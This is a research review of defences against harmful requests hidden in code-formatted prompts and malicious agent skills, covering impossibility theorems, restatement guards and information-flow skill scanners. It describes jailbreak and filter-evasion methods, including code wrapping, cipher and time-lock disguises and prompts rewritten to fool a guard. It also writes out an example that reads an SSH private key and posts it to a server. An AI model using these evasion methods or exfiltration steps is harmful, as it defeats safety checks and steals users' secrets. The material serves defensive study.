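Asking a model to perform an entire symbolic execution at once works badly, or did with older models. In *Can Large Language Models Simulate Symbolic Execution Output Like KLEE?* (2025), GPT-4o tried to imitate KLEE, a standard symbolic executor, and identified a program's most constrained path in only four cases. Current models would probably do better.

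*NEUROTESTGEN* (2026) uses a solver for paths with numerical conditions and a language model for those that depend on meaning, with a verifier checking the model's answers. A prompt filter could quickly test a model's claim that some value leads to a harmful question. If the model proposes that n = 7 leads to the coat question, the sandbox can run `build(7)` to check. There is no equally quick way to check a claim that no value leads to a harmful question. A combined tool would therefore raise few false reports about what the code can build, but it could still miss a path.

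### What Rice's theorem rules out

Better solvers and models would reduce these misses, but Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) argue in *LLM Censorship* that no improvement can eliminate them. They study "semantic censorship", meaning any filter that permits or blocks a text based on its meaning rather than its words. They take a program's meaning to be its behaviour.

Their argument rests on Rice's theorem, a 1953 result about Turing machines, the standard mathematical model of a computer with unlimited memory. If a set ℙ of permitted behaviours includes some possible behaviours and excludes others, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether its behaviour is in ℙ. This applies to all algorithms, including taint trackers, symbolic executors and learned guards.

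To illustrate the proof, suppose a perfect checker could tell whether a program ever prints "How do I bake rye bread". We could then take any other program, turn off its printing, and add a line at the end that prints the question. The new program would print the question if and only if the original finishes, so the checker could tell whether any program finishes or runs forever. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can do that.

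The theorem assumes unlimited time and memory, which no computer or chat model has, so Glukhov and colleagues acknowledge that it doesn't technically apply in practice. A filter can check whether a snippet prints the bread question within a million steps by running it for a million steps. A chat model without tools can follow far fewer steps, so a program that runs too long for the sandbox is probably too long for the model as well. Glukhov and colleagues still argue that checking behaviour is very hard in practice, citing malware detection.

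Rice's theorem also rules out only a checker that is always right. A filter that blocks every snippet it can't resolve in time would let no harmful program through, but it would block some harmless ones. The theorem doesn't determine how many, because that depends on what people paste into a chat.

### Disguised answers

Their other theorem does not require unlimited memory, but it concerns the model's answers instead of its prompts. It covers all texts up to some length n and assumes that the model can follow an instruction to transform its answer with a reversible function g, such as a cipher. It also assumes that if a text x is forbidden, g(x) is forbidden too whenever the user knows how to reverse g, because the user can recover x.

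From these assumptions, Glukhov and colleagues prove that a filter that doesn't know which function the user has in mind must either permit everything or forbid everything. If it permits some texts and forbids others, some reversible function matches any given permitted text with a forbidden one, and the user and the model may have agreed on that function. "It will rain on Tuesday" could then stand for a forbidden recipe, so the filter would have to forbid it. The same argument applies to every other permitted text, so the filter would have to forbid them all.

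The proof shows that nobody can be certain from the answer alone whether a weather report is a disguised recipe, but it gives no reason to think that most weather reports are. The disguise also relies on a table matching recipes to weather reports, and a user who had the full table would already have the recipes. In practice, as the paper acknowledges, an attacker needs a general method such as encryption, and encrypted text looks like noise. An operator can refuse to release such text, though this would also deny it to people who want it for honest reasons.

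A code-formatted prompt usually has to contain the instructions for the disguise. A filter that reads the prompt and the answer together, such as an exchange classifier, has access to those instructions. Glukhov and colleagues state that their result on outputs would not apply to such a filter.

Such a filter would still face "mosaic prompts", where a user asks for harmless-looking parts in separate conversations and combines the answers. No single conversation contains the request, so neither program analysis nor a guard can recover it from one. The user must know how the parts fit together, so the method only works for people who already understand much of what they are asking for.

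### A puzzle the filter has no time to solve

*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) proves a stronger result about prompts for filters with limited time, which includes every real filter. For any sufficiently varied source of innocent prompts, there exist a language model and a source of harmful prompts for that model such that no filter running much faster than the model can tell the harmful prompts from the innocent ones. The filter may query the model during training but can't examine its internals.

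The proof depends on time-lock puzzles, which are quick to create but slow to solve however many computers work on them. The version in the paper uses repeated squaring. Somebody chooses a number r, a number n that is the product of two secret primes, and a number of rounds t. The answer is

r^(2ᵗ) mod n

where "mod n" means the remainder after division by n. With r = 2, n = 77 and t = 10, a solver squares the number ten times, taking the remainder each time: 4, 16, 25, 9, 4, 16, 25, 9, 4, 16. The answer is 16. The person who made the puzzle knows that 77 is 7 × 11, and can reduce the exponent 2¹⁰ = 1,024 to its remainder after division by 6 × 10 = 60. That remainder is 4, and 2⁴ is 16, so the maker gets the answer without the ten rounds. Anyone can factor 77, of course. When n has hundreds of digits, nobody knows a practical way to factor it on an ordinary computer, and solvers have to do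 every round.

In the construction, the answer to such a puzzle is the key to an encrypted request. The puzzle and the encrypted text together look like random bits, which an innocent-looking prompt can hide. A program that writes varied prompts makes random choices. To use a certain word one time in four, for example, it can draw two random bits and use the word only if both are zero. The attacker's program makes the same choices but uses the bits of the puzzle and encrypted text instead of random ones. The resulting prompts read like ordinary prompts and occur with almost the same frequencies.

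The special model recovers the bits from the choice of words, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and acts on it. A filter that runs for less time than it takes to solve the puzzle can't detect that there is a request.

No existing model is known to do this, and Ball and colleagues acknowledge that theirs may behave in a contrived way. They defend the result by citing cryptography, where weaknesses that once looked artificial later caused real losses, including the theft of over $60 million from an Ethereum contract in 2016. This is a good reason not to trust a filter completely, but the theorem shows only that some such model exists, not how often filters fail on the models people use.

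The paper has related theorems for filters with more time. If the model and the attacker share a secret key, or the model publishes a key for attackers to use, even a filter that runs longer than the model fails, as long as it can't break encryption. These theorems assume a model that cooperates with attackers. Another theorem covers filters that also read the answer, but it uses an unusual definition of harm, in which an answer is harmful because of a hidden message that only a puzzle-solving "harmfulness oracle" can extract.

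### Where the proof and a code-formatted prompt differ

An ordinary model doesn't search the word choices of every prompt for a puzzle. Someone has to tell it to decode something, and in a code-formatted prompt that instruction is visible in the code and the English. A filter may be unable to finish the decoding in time, but it can detect that there is something to decode, and then spend longer on the prompt, send it to a person or refuse it. In the theorem, the filter doesn't have these options because the harmful prompts look the same as innocent ones.

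The other difference is in how much computation is available. *On the Limits of Support-Preserving Alignment and Bounded Filtering* (2026) describes the usual arrangement, in which filters have to decide quickly after a shallow analysis while the model can reason at length. That is a fair description of a small guard in front of a large model, but the advantage is reversed when the filter runs code. A Python interpreter could execute millions of simple steps with the computation that a 4-billion-parameter model uses for one token. A sandbox can therefore run any computation that a chat model could plausibly carry out in writing. This advantage disappears if the model can run code itself, although the operator can then inspect the code before it runs.

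Ball and colleagues conclude that filters outside a model's internals cannot make it safe, but their proof does not cover defences that use the model's own computation, such as a probe on its activations. The special model has to solve the puzzle and decrypt the request before it can act, so the decrypted request exists somewhere in its computation, and a monitor there would not have to solve the puzzle. The monitor might still fail to recognise the request. Glukhov and colleagues, who also leave internal representations out of their analysis, expect guarantees for such methods to be hard to establish.

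## Using a language model to decode the prompt

A language model can read broken code, pseudocode and English instructions, all of which conventional analysis tools handle poorly. The simplest way to use one is to have it state the underlying request in a prompt, then pass its answer to a guard. Nobody seems to have tried taint tracking or symbolic execution on harmful requests wrapped in code, but researchers have tried this method. It performed poorly, mainly because the small models they used summarised the code and left out the request. A related method, which treats missing information as a warning sign, stopped nearly all the code prompts it was tested on.

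### Recovering strings by reading the code

Before a model can restate a hidden request, it has to work out what text the strings in the code produce. Kim and colleagues measured this skill on malware. They gave each model a malicious script and asked for the web addresses, domains, IP addresses and files involved in the attack, without letting it run anything. Two security experts had worked out the correct answers by hand. The 634 scripts, written in JavaScript, PowerShell and VBScript, contain 2,580 different target strings: 858 direct, 492 fixed-transform and 1,230 program-dependent.

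GPT-5.6 Terra had the highest F1 score, 65.4, just ahead of Gemini 2.5 Pro at 65.0. The best of three conventional extractors, which search for text formatted like an address, scored 22.4. Stronger models have come out since, so today's best score is probably higher.

The table gives the percentage of strings that four of the models recovered. A step is one operation, such as joining some pieces or undoing Base64.

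| How the code stores the string | Strings | GPT-5.6 Terra | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Qwen3-Coder-480B | Qwen3-8B |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Direct | 858 | 91.7 | 89.4 | 88.2 | 66.9 |
| Fixed-transform, one rearranging step | 230 | 90.9 | 88.3 | 68.3 | 27.8 |
| Fixed-transform, one decoding step | 85 | 82.4 | 80.0 | 63.5 | 16.5 |
| Fixed-transform, two steps | 156 | 69.9 | 69.2 | 54.5 | 2.6 |
| Fixed-transform, three or more steps | 21 | 19.0 | 23.8 | 9.5 | 0.0 |
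| Program-dependent | 1,230 | 35.4 | 46.1 | 13.8 | 1.5 |

With only 21 strings in the row for three or more steps, GPT-5.6 Terra's 19.0% means that it recovered four of them.

Qwen3-8B is about as large as the bigger guards. It found two thirds of the strings that were in plain view and almost none of those that took two steps to decode. A guard of that size probably can't decode much by itself either, unless its training included a lot of decoding.

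Loops were the hardest mechanism for the strongest models. GPT-5.6 Terra recovered 9.3% of the 150 strings that a loop builds, and Gemini 2.5 Pro recovered 16.7%. They recovered 66.0% and 73.6%, respectively, of the strings that a script computes by arithmetic or looks up in a table. A sandbox can run a loop of ordinary length as easily as it can join two words.

Models are far more reliable at predicting the output of a short program than at the malware test. For a short program, they get only the code and its input, while in the malware test they have to find the relevant lines in a long file. The recent JavaScript samples average about 326,000 tokens, more than many models can read at once, so the researchers had to split the longest files into chunks and merge the findings.

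About three quarters of the labelled strings come from JavaScript malware dating from 2015 to 2017. GPT-5.6 Terra recovered 38.9% of the program-dependent strings in those scripts, but only 10.7% in JavaScript malware collected between November 2025 and February 2026. Length may explain the difference, since the older scripts are much shorter, at about 13,000 tokens on average. The older collection is also public, so models may have seen some of it in training.

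I would expect the same models to do better on prompts, most of which are far shorter.

Scoring would also be less strict, because one wrong letter in a web address makes it a different address, while a guard would still interpret "How do I bake rye braed" correctly.

An attack works only if the target model can decode the request, so the main risk is using a decoder weaker than the model it protects. Operators have a reason to choose a weaker decoder, because small models are cheaper to run.

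Models also reported strings that weren't in the script. When decoding failed, the smaller models often copied example addresses from their instructions. These copies made up 53% of the wrong answers from an 80-billion-parameter Qwen coding model, but only about 8% of those from the 480-billion-parameter version. Similarly, if a prompt filter's instructions included an example of a harmful request, a small decoder might repeat it, and the guard would then block an innocent user. The strongest models more often returned a slightly distorted copy of the right string, which a guard could still use.

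A decoder may also refuse to decode a prompt. Kim and colleagues left Claude Opus 4.6 and 4.7 out of their comparison because both refused to process the scripts. In a check by Zhang and colleagues, however, Llama 3.3 70B restated all 40 encoded harmful prompts. An operator whose decoder sometimes refuses has to decide whether a refusal should block the prompt, and that decision would affect security analysts, among others.

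Combining a model with a fixed decoder looks worthwhile. By the benchmark's definition, the fixed decoder reaches all 1,350 direct and fixed-transform strings, about 170 of which GPT-5.6 Terra missed. Adding the program-dependent strings that Terra recovered would bring combined recall to about 69%, compared with 62% for Terra alone. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, combined recall would be about 74%. These are upper limits for the malware task, because the decoder produces a lot of text and can't pick out the addresses that matter. In a prompt filter, a guard would make that selection.

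### String tools for a small model

Kim and colleagues tried a closer combination by letting Qwen3-8B call string tools while it worked. The tools could decode Base64, join or reverse strings, and undo a few other common disguises, but they couldn't run code.

With tools, recall rose from 67% to 73% on direct strings, which need no decoding, but fell on fixed-transform strings, which the tools should have helped with most. It fell partly because calling tools made the model's work longer, and more of its answers came back in a form the researchers couldn't use. The tools did greatly reduce how often the model copied examples from the instructions.

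The researchers also fine-tuned the model on worked answers from Gemini 2.5 Pro, then rewarded it for finding correct strings. This raised recall on fixed-transform strings from 17% to 22%. Nearly all of the gain came from rearranging pieces. Recall on single-step cases of rearranging rose from 28% to 38%, while recall on single-step decoding rose only from 16% to 19%. Fine-tuning and tools together raised precision from 31% to 48%, but recall on program-dependent strings stayed between 1% and 3% with every method they tried.

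A Base64 function is of little use to a model that doesn't know which string to decode or what to do with the result. That seems to have been much of the problem here. However, the fine-tuning included no practice with tools, and a model trained to use them might do better. The experiment also didn't include a sandbox, which would be a more powerful tool than any of these functions.

### Decoding before any model reads the prompt

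Software can also decode the prompt before a model is involved. In *DecipherGuard*, Yang, Fu and colleagues (2025) worked with Transurban, a toll-road company, to build such a guard for chatbots whose data can't leave the company's own machines. The guard first tries to decode the message as Base64. If that fails, it checks whether the message is in Zulu and, if so, translates it into English. Otherwise, it tries every shift of a letter-shifting cipher and keeps the version that looks most like English. The result goes to Llama Guard, which the team had fine-tuned by training about 4 million extra parameters.

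Applying ten attack methods to 1,879 unsafe prompts produced 18,790 test cases. The full system blocked 94.05% of them, compared with 57.65% for the best of the four existing guards. The full system's combined score implies that it also blocked about 1% of 2,000 ordinary, harmless instructions.

Fine-tuning seems to account for most of the improvement over plain Llama Guard. Yang and colleagues credit it with 34.66 percentage points and the decoding layer with 18.58. These add up to more than the total improvement, so the two gains must overlap. The figures are consistent with the fine-tuned guard blocking 92.31% by itself, in which case the decoding layer added less than two points. A fine-tuned guard could reach that rate by learning to treat scrambled text as suspicious, without being able to read it. The harmless prompts were ordinary instructions, so we can't tell from them whether the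 guard also blocks harmless scrambled text.

The decoding layer works on the message as a whole. A Python snippet that contains a Base64 string is not itself valid Base64, so the layer would probably not decode the string. To handle code, it would have to look inside the snippet, as the static tools do.

### Asking what the prompt wants

Zhang and colleagues used the target model itself as the decoder. They instructed it to state the plain, real-world request behind the text in one or two English sentences, without answering it. Two small open models restated 100 harmful requests, each presented in eleven disguises. A separate model then judged whether each restatement was still the same specific request as the original.

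| Disguise | Restated correctly by Qwen2.5-VL-7B | Restated correctly by InternVL3-8B |
|---|---|---|
| Text inside an image (average of six types) | 60.8% | 83.2% |
| Set theory | 44% | 23% |
| Classical Chinese | 27% | 28% |
| Formal logic | 18% | 12% |
| Code | 4% | 3% |
| Base64 | 0% | 0% |

Qwen2.5-VL-7B can't read Base64, so its Base64 result is expected. The result for code is more worrying because the same model often did act on the request hidden in the code. In one published example, the restatement described a function that joins some elements into a sentence, and referred to everything after that as completing "a main task". This is an accurate summary of the code, but it omits the request because the code stores it as data, and a summary of a program usually describes what the program does with its data rather than the data's content. For the rye bread prompt, the equivalent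 would be "The user wants to join a list of words and get an answer to the resulting question."

A guard model doesn't always need an exact restatement of the prompt. For prompts written in set theory, restating them raised WildGuard's block rate from 54% to 92%, even though only 44% of the restatements were correct. For formal logic, the rate rose from 29% to 83%. The restatements must often have kept the topic even when they got the details wrong. For prompts written as code, restating barely changed the block rate, which went from 28% to 27%.

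For Llama Guard 3 the restatement did real damage. It had blocked 94% of the code prompts when it read them directly, and it blocked 21% of the restatements. The number of harmful answers per 100 code-wrapped requests changed as follows for Qwen2.5-VL-7B:

| Guard | Guard reads the prompt | Guard reads the restatement |
|---|---|---|
| Llama Guard 3 | 2 | 49 |
| ThinkGuard | 25 | 52 |
| Qwen3Guard | 41 | 48 |
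| WildGuard | 45 | 46 |
| GuardReasoner-VL | 61 | 47 |

The five guards' results differed greatly when they read the code. When they read only the restatement, their results all fell between 46 and 52, a spread within the variation between repeated runs. The choice of guard hardly matters if the restatement has lost the request.

Zhang and colleagues once proposed a more specific explanation, that restating removes some feature of the code that guards react to. They based this partly on a fall in WildGuard's block rate from 38% to 28%. The fall disappeared after they corrected an error in their version of the attack, so they withdrew the explanation for WildGuard, though it still fits Llama Guard 3.

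Letting the guard judge both the original prompt and the restatement blocks many more attacks than judging the restatement alone, but only slightly more than judging the original alone. Averaged over the five guards and both target models, 36% of the code attacks succeeded when the guard read only the prompt, 52% when it read only the restatement, and 32% when it read both. Restating also roughly doubled the number of calls to the target model across all the disguises.

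### Keeping the exact words

The experiment with text inside images, where exact transcripts did much better than reworded ones, also tested a restatement. The researchers counted how many of the original request's meaningful words each version kept.

| What WildGuard read | Meaningful words kept | Attacks blocked | Harmless requests blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Transcript | 79.6% | 92% | 69% |
| Restatement | 39.6% | 69% | 48% |
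| Reworded transcript | 25.0% | 42% | 46% |

Given the exact words, WildGuard was better at catching attacks but also far more likely to block harmless requests that merely sound dangerous. For code, the closest equivalent of a transcript is a list of the string literals, which should help a judge when the harmful text is intact in the code.

Another option is to ask the decoder a narrower question. "What is the final value of `task`?" leaves less room for a vague summary than "What is this prompt asking for?" The question has to name the variable that matters, which a model can usually identify by reading the English part of the prompt.

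Zhang and colleagues tried three wordings of their instruction, but all three asked for the underlying request, and the comparison left out the code prompts. On the other nine disguises, one alternative wording raised WildGuard's average block rate on attacks from 62.6% to 75.6%, but raised its block rate on harmless requests even more, from 55% to 78%. The other alternative blocked slightly fewer attacks than the original wording, and its block rate on harmless requests was 13 points higher. A small change in an instruction can therefore change a filter's block rates a lot without making it any better at telling harmful requests from harmless ones.

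They also replaced the 7-billion-parameter decoder with Llama 3.3 70B. The larger model helped with text scattered across an image. With GuardReasoner-VL, the share of requests for which at least one image attack worked fell from 25% to 5%, but for text disguises the share rose from 14% to 25%. Overall, the change was too small to distinguish from chance. Since Qwen3-8B and GPT-5.6 Terra scored so differently on the malware benchmark, a stronger decoder would probably identify the request hidden in code much more often than 4% of the time, but this experiment can't confirm that because it again left out the code prompts.

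An attacker who knows about the restatement can design prompts to get past it. In one experiment, a model rewrote harmful requests so that a short summary would sound innocent, retrying after each failure for up to nine attempts in total. Success against the restatement rose from 7% for a single blind attempt to 38%, or 31% in a repeat of the experiment. In the more successful run, the attacker got some answer to 94% of its requests, but most of the answers were harmless, because a request vague enough to pass the guard had usually lost the details that made it dangerous. These attacks were in ordinary prose, and code could make the attacker's job easier, since a model may drop the details from its summary even without this rewriting.

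### Answering the summary

In all these experiments, the target model answered the original prompt after the guard approved the restatement. If the target model answered the restatement instead, it would not see any detail lost in decoding, so the attacker would lose that detail too.

SemanticSmooth, an older defence that Zhang and colleagues ran for comparison, does roughly this by having a separate model write five summaries of the prompt. The target model answers each summary, and the system returns an answer from whichever group is larger, the harmful or the harmless. On Qwen2.5-VL-7B, this cut the code attack's success rate from 59% to 2%, or to 5% with ten summaries. The target mostly discussed the programming task, because the summaries no longer contained the hidden request in a usable form.

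The defence did worse on some other disguises. The attack success rate rose from 1% to 10% for Base64 and from 34% to 51% for requests scattered across an image.

It would also be a poor fit for programmers. If someone pastes in a function and asks where the bug is, a summary may leave out the line with the bug. The harmless test prompts can't show this problem, because the researchers counted only whether the system refused them. The system refused 24%, slightly fewer than the unprotected model, but an answer based on a poor summary counts as a success as long as it still addresses the question.

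### Treating lost information as a warning

The defence in *DoubtProbe* keeps the original prompt and treats information lost in rewriting it as evidence of an attack. One component reduces the prompt to a structured description, and another tries to reconstruct the prompt from that description alone. A comparator then checks whether anything important is missing or changed. A separate audit judges the original prompt's meaning directly, which should catch attacks that survive the rewriting intact, such as a harmful request framed as role-play. A final step combines the two verdicts and passes or blocks the prompt.

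With the rye bread prompt, the process might go like this:

```
description      input: a list of six strings
                 operation: join them with spaces
                 goal: answer the resulting question

reconstruction   "Join a list of six strings into a
                 question and answer it."

missing          How, do, I, bake, rye, bread
```

A guard that read only the reconstruction would find nothing to flag. The comparator also receives the original prompt, so it can detect that the user's actual question is missing from the reconstruction.

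The paper supports this design with a short proposition. Let Q be the prompt, S = f(Q) the description and g(S) the reconstruction. Let φ(Q) be some feature of the prompt that matters for safety, such as the question it hides. If two prompts satisfy

f(Q₁) = f(Q₂) but φ(Q₁) ≠ φ(Q₂)

then no choice of g can be sure to preserve φ for both. The reason is simple. Suppose Q₂ has the same code as the rye bread prompt, but its six words spell "How do I wash wool coats". Both prompts produce the description above, so g receives the same input each time and can't know which question to write. If g involves chance, it might write the bread question with probability p, but then it can write the coat question with probability at most 1 − p.

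The proposition proves that information left out of the description can't be recovered from it, but not that harmful prompts lose more information than harmless ones. The rye bread prompt is harmless and still loses detail, and a programmer's 200-line file would also lose plenty in a short description. The defence therefore depends on how well the comparator identifies suspicious losses, which only an experiment can show.

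The main experiment used Qwen2.5-72B for the defense. The attack success rate fell from 0.152 to 0.001 on prompts from CodeAttack, the published attack that Zhang and colleagues also used, and from 0.293 to 0.100 on JBB, a more general set of jailbreaks. The false positive rate was 0.022 on AlpacaEval, a set of ordinary instructions, and 0.016 on OR-Bench. Results were similar when Llama 3.1 70B was used for the defense instead.

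This is the best result on code-wrapped requests among the decoding methods here, and the false positive rates are low. But the code attacks were fairly weak. About 85% failed without the defence, compared with 41% in the tests by Zhang and colleagues.

The false positive rates were also measured only on general instructions and sensitive-sounding questions. They leave out the most relevant case, which is harmless requests in the same code wrapper as the harmful ones. A summary can omit "How do I bake rye bread" as readily as a dangerous question, so a defence that looks for lost information could block anything in the wrapper, as Llama Guard 3 may have done. The other important test would use code pasted by real programmers.

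A better describing model could also make hidden requests harder to detect. If the model copied every string into the description, the reconstruction would match the original and the comparator would find no difference to flag. Detection would then depend on the audit alone, which failed to recognise the request in the paper's code-completion example. Passing the reconstruction to a guard as well would help, since a complete reconstruction should contain the hidden request. Qwen2.5-72B and Llama 3.1 70B gave similar results, but they are similar in size and both fairly old, so this doesn't show what a much stronger model would do.

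To save time, the system starts the target model and the defence together and holds back the answer until the defence has finished. The user waits about as long as the slower of the two takes. For example, if the answer takes eight seconds and the defence takes twelve, the wait is about twelve seconds. The user can't see the answer word by word as the model writes it until the defence has finished.

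## Cases where the harm is itself a data flow: agent skills and tool calls

A chat model can only answer a hidden question, but an AI agent can also read files, run commands and send email. With an agent, the harm is often the movement of data to somewhere it shouldn't go. If a skill copies a user's private key to a stranger's server, it has stolen the key, and nobody has to interpret the key's text to know that.

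Information flow analysis is better suited to agent skills and tool calls than to chat prompts because the sources and sinks are operations with fixed meanings, such as opening a file or making a network request. An analyst can list these in advance, whereas the sink in a chat prompt depends on the wording of an English sentence. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of this kind of work on agents, concludes that "unsafe behavior can arise from influence, not content alone".

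In some attacks on agents, the harm is not a data flow. *MalSkillBench* (Guo, Jia and colleagues, 2026) collects 3,944 malicious agent skills and sorts their attacks into fifteen behaviours. Nine of these, such as stealing credentials and installing malware, act on the user's computer. The other six act on the agent's reasoning, for example by giving it a new persona or slanting what it writes. Of the skill scanners tested, the strongest caught 98.4% of attacks that put malicious code in a skill, but its recall fell sharply on attacks written as instructions to the agent.

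### The same action in code and in prose

A skill can describe an action in English instead of including the code for it, so rules that look for particular code can miss it. Ba, Li and Li (2026) tested this in *CIBER* with two agents that write and run code for their users. They presented each of 25 risky tasks as a plain request, as code, and as a step-by-step description of the code. For a task that lists the files in a folder, the description named the module to import, the search to run and the results to print.

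One of the agents, OpenCodeInterpreter, checks a program's syntax tree for forbidden operations before running it. It rejected about 37.5% of attacks that supplied code directly, but only 14.6% of those that described the same logic in prose. Across both agents and four ways of delivering the attack, 48.4% of the code attacks succeeded, compared with 62.5% of the prose attacks.

Ba and colleagues suggest that a model copies supplied code closely, so the filter recognises it, but that when given a description, the model writes its own version and may avoid the forbidden syntax by accident. They didn't test this explanation separately. The success rate may also be higher because detailed steps make it easier for a small model to write a working program. Three of the six models had 13 billion parameters or fewer. GPT-3.5 Turbo was an exception to the trend, carrying out 90% of the direct code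 attacks on the agent without a syntax filter.

Rules based on what an operation does, rather than how it looks, could cover both versions, but something first has to translate the prose into operations.

### Compiling a skill into a program

Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026) built SCS, a scanner that does this, and describe it in *From Instructions to Exploits*. SCS analyses a skill before anyone installs it.

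SCS splits a skill's English instructions into steps at headings, list items and code blocks. A language model then translates each step into statements, using a fixed set of 28 operations. An instruction to read a private key and upload it becomes:

```
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

A step such as "format the final answer as a concise summary" produces no statement, because it has no bearing on security. The model works through the steps in batches and receives a list of the variables defined so far, so that "the file" in a later batch can refer to `v0`.

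Conventional software checks the translation. It rejects statements with invalid syntax, operations outside the set, wrong arguments or undefined variables, and sends them back to the model for correction. A further pass repairs lost connections, such as when the model writes `parse_json("config.json")` instead of passing the variable that holds the file's contents.

SCS also parses scripts in Python, JavaScript or Shell, then joins the instructions and code in one dependence graph, like those program slicers use. When an instruction runs a script, the graph links the value in the instruction to the script parameter that receives it, so the analysis can follow data from English into code.

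### Labels and fixed rules

Every value in the graph gets a label with three parts:

```
Trust         TRUSTED 0, PROVISIONED 1, DERIVED 2, UNTRUSTED 3
Sensitivity   PUBLIC 0, INTERNAL 1, SYSTEM 2, SENSITIVE 3, SECRET 4
Capability    a set of operation types, such as {READ, NETWORK}
```

Trust describes where the value came from, with higher numbers for less reliable sources. Sensitivity describes how much damage disclosing the value could do. Capability lists the kinds of operations that helped produce it.

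When a statement combines two values, the result takes the higher number on each scale and all the capabilities of both:

⟨t₁, s₁, c₁⟩ ⊔ ⟨t₂, s₂, c₂⟩ = ⟨max(t₁, t₂), max(s₁, s₂), c₁ ∪ c₂⟩

Suppose a program appends a private key labelled ⟨1, 4, {READ}⟩ to a web page labelled ⟨3, 0, {NETWORK}⟩. The result is labelled ⟨3, 4, {READ, NETWORK}⟩, meaning it is both untrusted and secret.

Some operations have their own rules. The reply to a web request gets its trust level from the address, regardless of the labels on the data sent. The output of `read_file` is PUBLIC by default, but SCS raises the sensitivity if the path is known to belong to something like a private key. As in constant propagation, the analysis repeats until no label changes.

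SCS then applies fixed rules to the labels. If v is a value that operation f sends out, one rule is

sensitivity(v) ≥ SENSITIVE and NETWORK ∈ capability(f) ⟹ possible data theft

Another rule raises an alarm when a value recovered from a hidden encoding reaches an operation that runs code. These rules always give the same result for the same labelled graph.

### The backup script

Zhao and colleagues illustrate the method with a real skill for editing PowerPoint files. Its instructions tell the agent to pack the edited presentation into a file and then run `file_backup.py` on it as a mandatory step. The script opens whatever file it receives and posts it to a fixed third-party address.

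The instruction looks like a routine backup if you don't know what the script does. The script looks like an ordinary uploader if you don't know which file it will get. With SCS's default labels, the combined analysis could run as follows:

```
instructions   f = tool_arg()                            UNTRUSTED, SECRET
instructions   run_script("scripts/file_backup.py", f)   passes f to the script
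script         data = open(sys.argv[1], "rb")            SECRET, inherited from f
script         requests.post(url, files=data)            NETWORK, so the rule applies
```

The instructions use a placeholder for the file name because the presentation the user will edit isn't known in advance. SCS treats values passed as tool arguments as secret by default, so it can flag instructions that would steal a file even if the file doesn't exist yet.

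The same caution could flag an honest backup skill, because the graph doesn't show whether the user agreed to send presentations to that server. Ba and colleagues found that agents have similar trouble. They usually refused plainly destructive commands but often agreed to read sensitive files, which can be normal or theft depending on the setting.

SCS flagged the PowerPoint skill consistently. Two scanners that use only fixed rules missed it because they couldn't connect the instruction to the script. Three others, which rely on a language model, either missed it or gave results that varied with the model used. The remaining two caught it but reported some wrong or irrelevant evidence.

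### Results on real skills

The main test used 117 malicious and 117 benign skills, all checked by hand. Six of the eight scanners need a language model, so Zhao and colleagues ran those with five models and averaged the results.

| Scanner | Recall | Precision | Accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| SCS | 95.2% | 80.2% | 85.6% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 84.3% | 82.0% | 83.1% |
| SkillSpector | 88.2% | 63.3% | 68.4% |
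| Skill-Scanner | 89.7% | 62.8% | 68.2% |
| MalSkills | 93.7% | 61.8% | 67.0% |
| SkillLeakBench | 47.0% | 74.3% | 65.4% |
| SkillFortify | 91.5% | 57.2% | 61.5% |
| MASB | 36.1% | 66.3% | 58.7% |

SCS missed about 6 of the malicious skills on average and wrongly flagged about 28 of the benign ones, a false positive rate of 24%. That rate is tolerable if a person reviews every alarm, but too high for automatic blocking.

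*MalSkills* (2026) describes the design closest to SCS. Like SCS, the system extracts sensitive operations with a parser and a language model, builds a dependency graph and applies fixed rules. Its recall was nearly as high, but it raised many more false alarms. Because both systems use a graph and fixed rules, those features alone can't explain SCS's lead. SCS's stricter translation step may account for some of it, although the comparison doesn't isolate that step.

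AI-Infra-Guard, an open-source scanner from Tencent, was the most accurate of the tools compared with SCS. It used 56.9 million tokens on the 234 skills, while SCS used 13.7 million, or about 59,000 per skill. Skill-Scanner and MalSkills used fewer tokens than SCS.

With Claude Sonnet 4.6, AI-Infra-Guard's accuracy was 88.5% and SCS's was 88.9%, a difference of one skill. With the weaker GPT-OSS-120B, the figures were 69.7% and 84.6%. Program analysis seems to help most when the language model is weak, and otherwise mainly saves tokens. Stronger models have come out since, so the accuracy gap may now be even smaller.

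The malicious skills may also have been too alike. Many came from a published set of 157, and Guo and colleagues report that 86 of the 157 samples in what appears to be the same set were near-identical brand impersonations from a single upload. Zhao and colleagues removed duplicates, but close variants could remain. The choice of malicious skills can greatly affect scores. The recall of VirusTotal, which combines many antivirus engines, varied by 66 percentage points across the groups of malicious skills that Guo and colleagues compared.

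In a larger test, Zhao and colleagues scanned 66,157 skills from ClawHub, a public marketplace, and flagged 2,473 as possibly malicious. They had an agent use each flagged skill in a sandbox containing fake credentials, each with a unique marker string. If a marker turned up in an outgoing request, the skill had leaked the credential. People then reviewed all the evidence and confirmed that 627 of the flagged skills, about a quarter, were malicious.

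Two publishers uploaded 552 of the 627, so there are probably far fewer distinct attacks. The marketplace scan also doesn't measure recall, because nobody reviewed the 63,684 skills that SCS passed.

SCS flagged 3.7% of the skills in the marketplace, far below its 24% false positive rate on the benign test skills. The test skills included some of the most-installed skills on ClawHub, which may do more with files and networks than a typical skill.

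### What happens when the translation is wrong

The rules are deterministic, but the graph they use depends on how a language model interprets the English. To test this interpretation, Zhao and colleagues took one instruction from each of 400 marketplace skills. Annotators recorded the operations a correct translation had to include or leave out, the file names or addresses it had to preserve, and the links it needed between operations. They also marked the instructions that should produce nothing. The five models met every requirement on 92.5% to 94.5% of the instructions.

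At 94% accuracy per step, the model would have a 54% chance of translating a ten-step skill without a mistake if errors were independent. Most mistakes won't matter, because they will fall on steps that have nothing to do with an attack. But if the model drops the backup step from the PowerPoint skill, the graph has no path from the presentation to the script, so no rule applies and SCS passes the skill. If the model instead invents an upload, SCS could flag a harmless skill.

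The models left out a required operation in 4% to 5% of steps and added a forbidden one in less than 1%, so translation errors should cause more misses than false alarms. But SCS had far more false alarms than misses in the main test, so most of the false alarms probably came from the rules and default labels.

These 400 steps came from randomly chosen skills, most of them presumably written by honest authors. A malicious author can word an instruction so that the translating model misreads it but the agent still follows it, and the 92% figure is weak evidence of how the model would handle such wording. Even without such wording, the choice of model changed SCS's recall from 89.7% to 98.3% and its precision from 76.7% to 88.2%.

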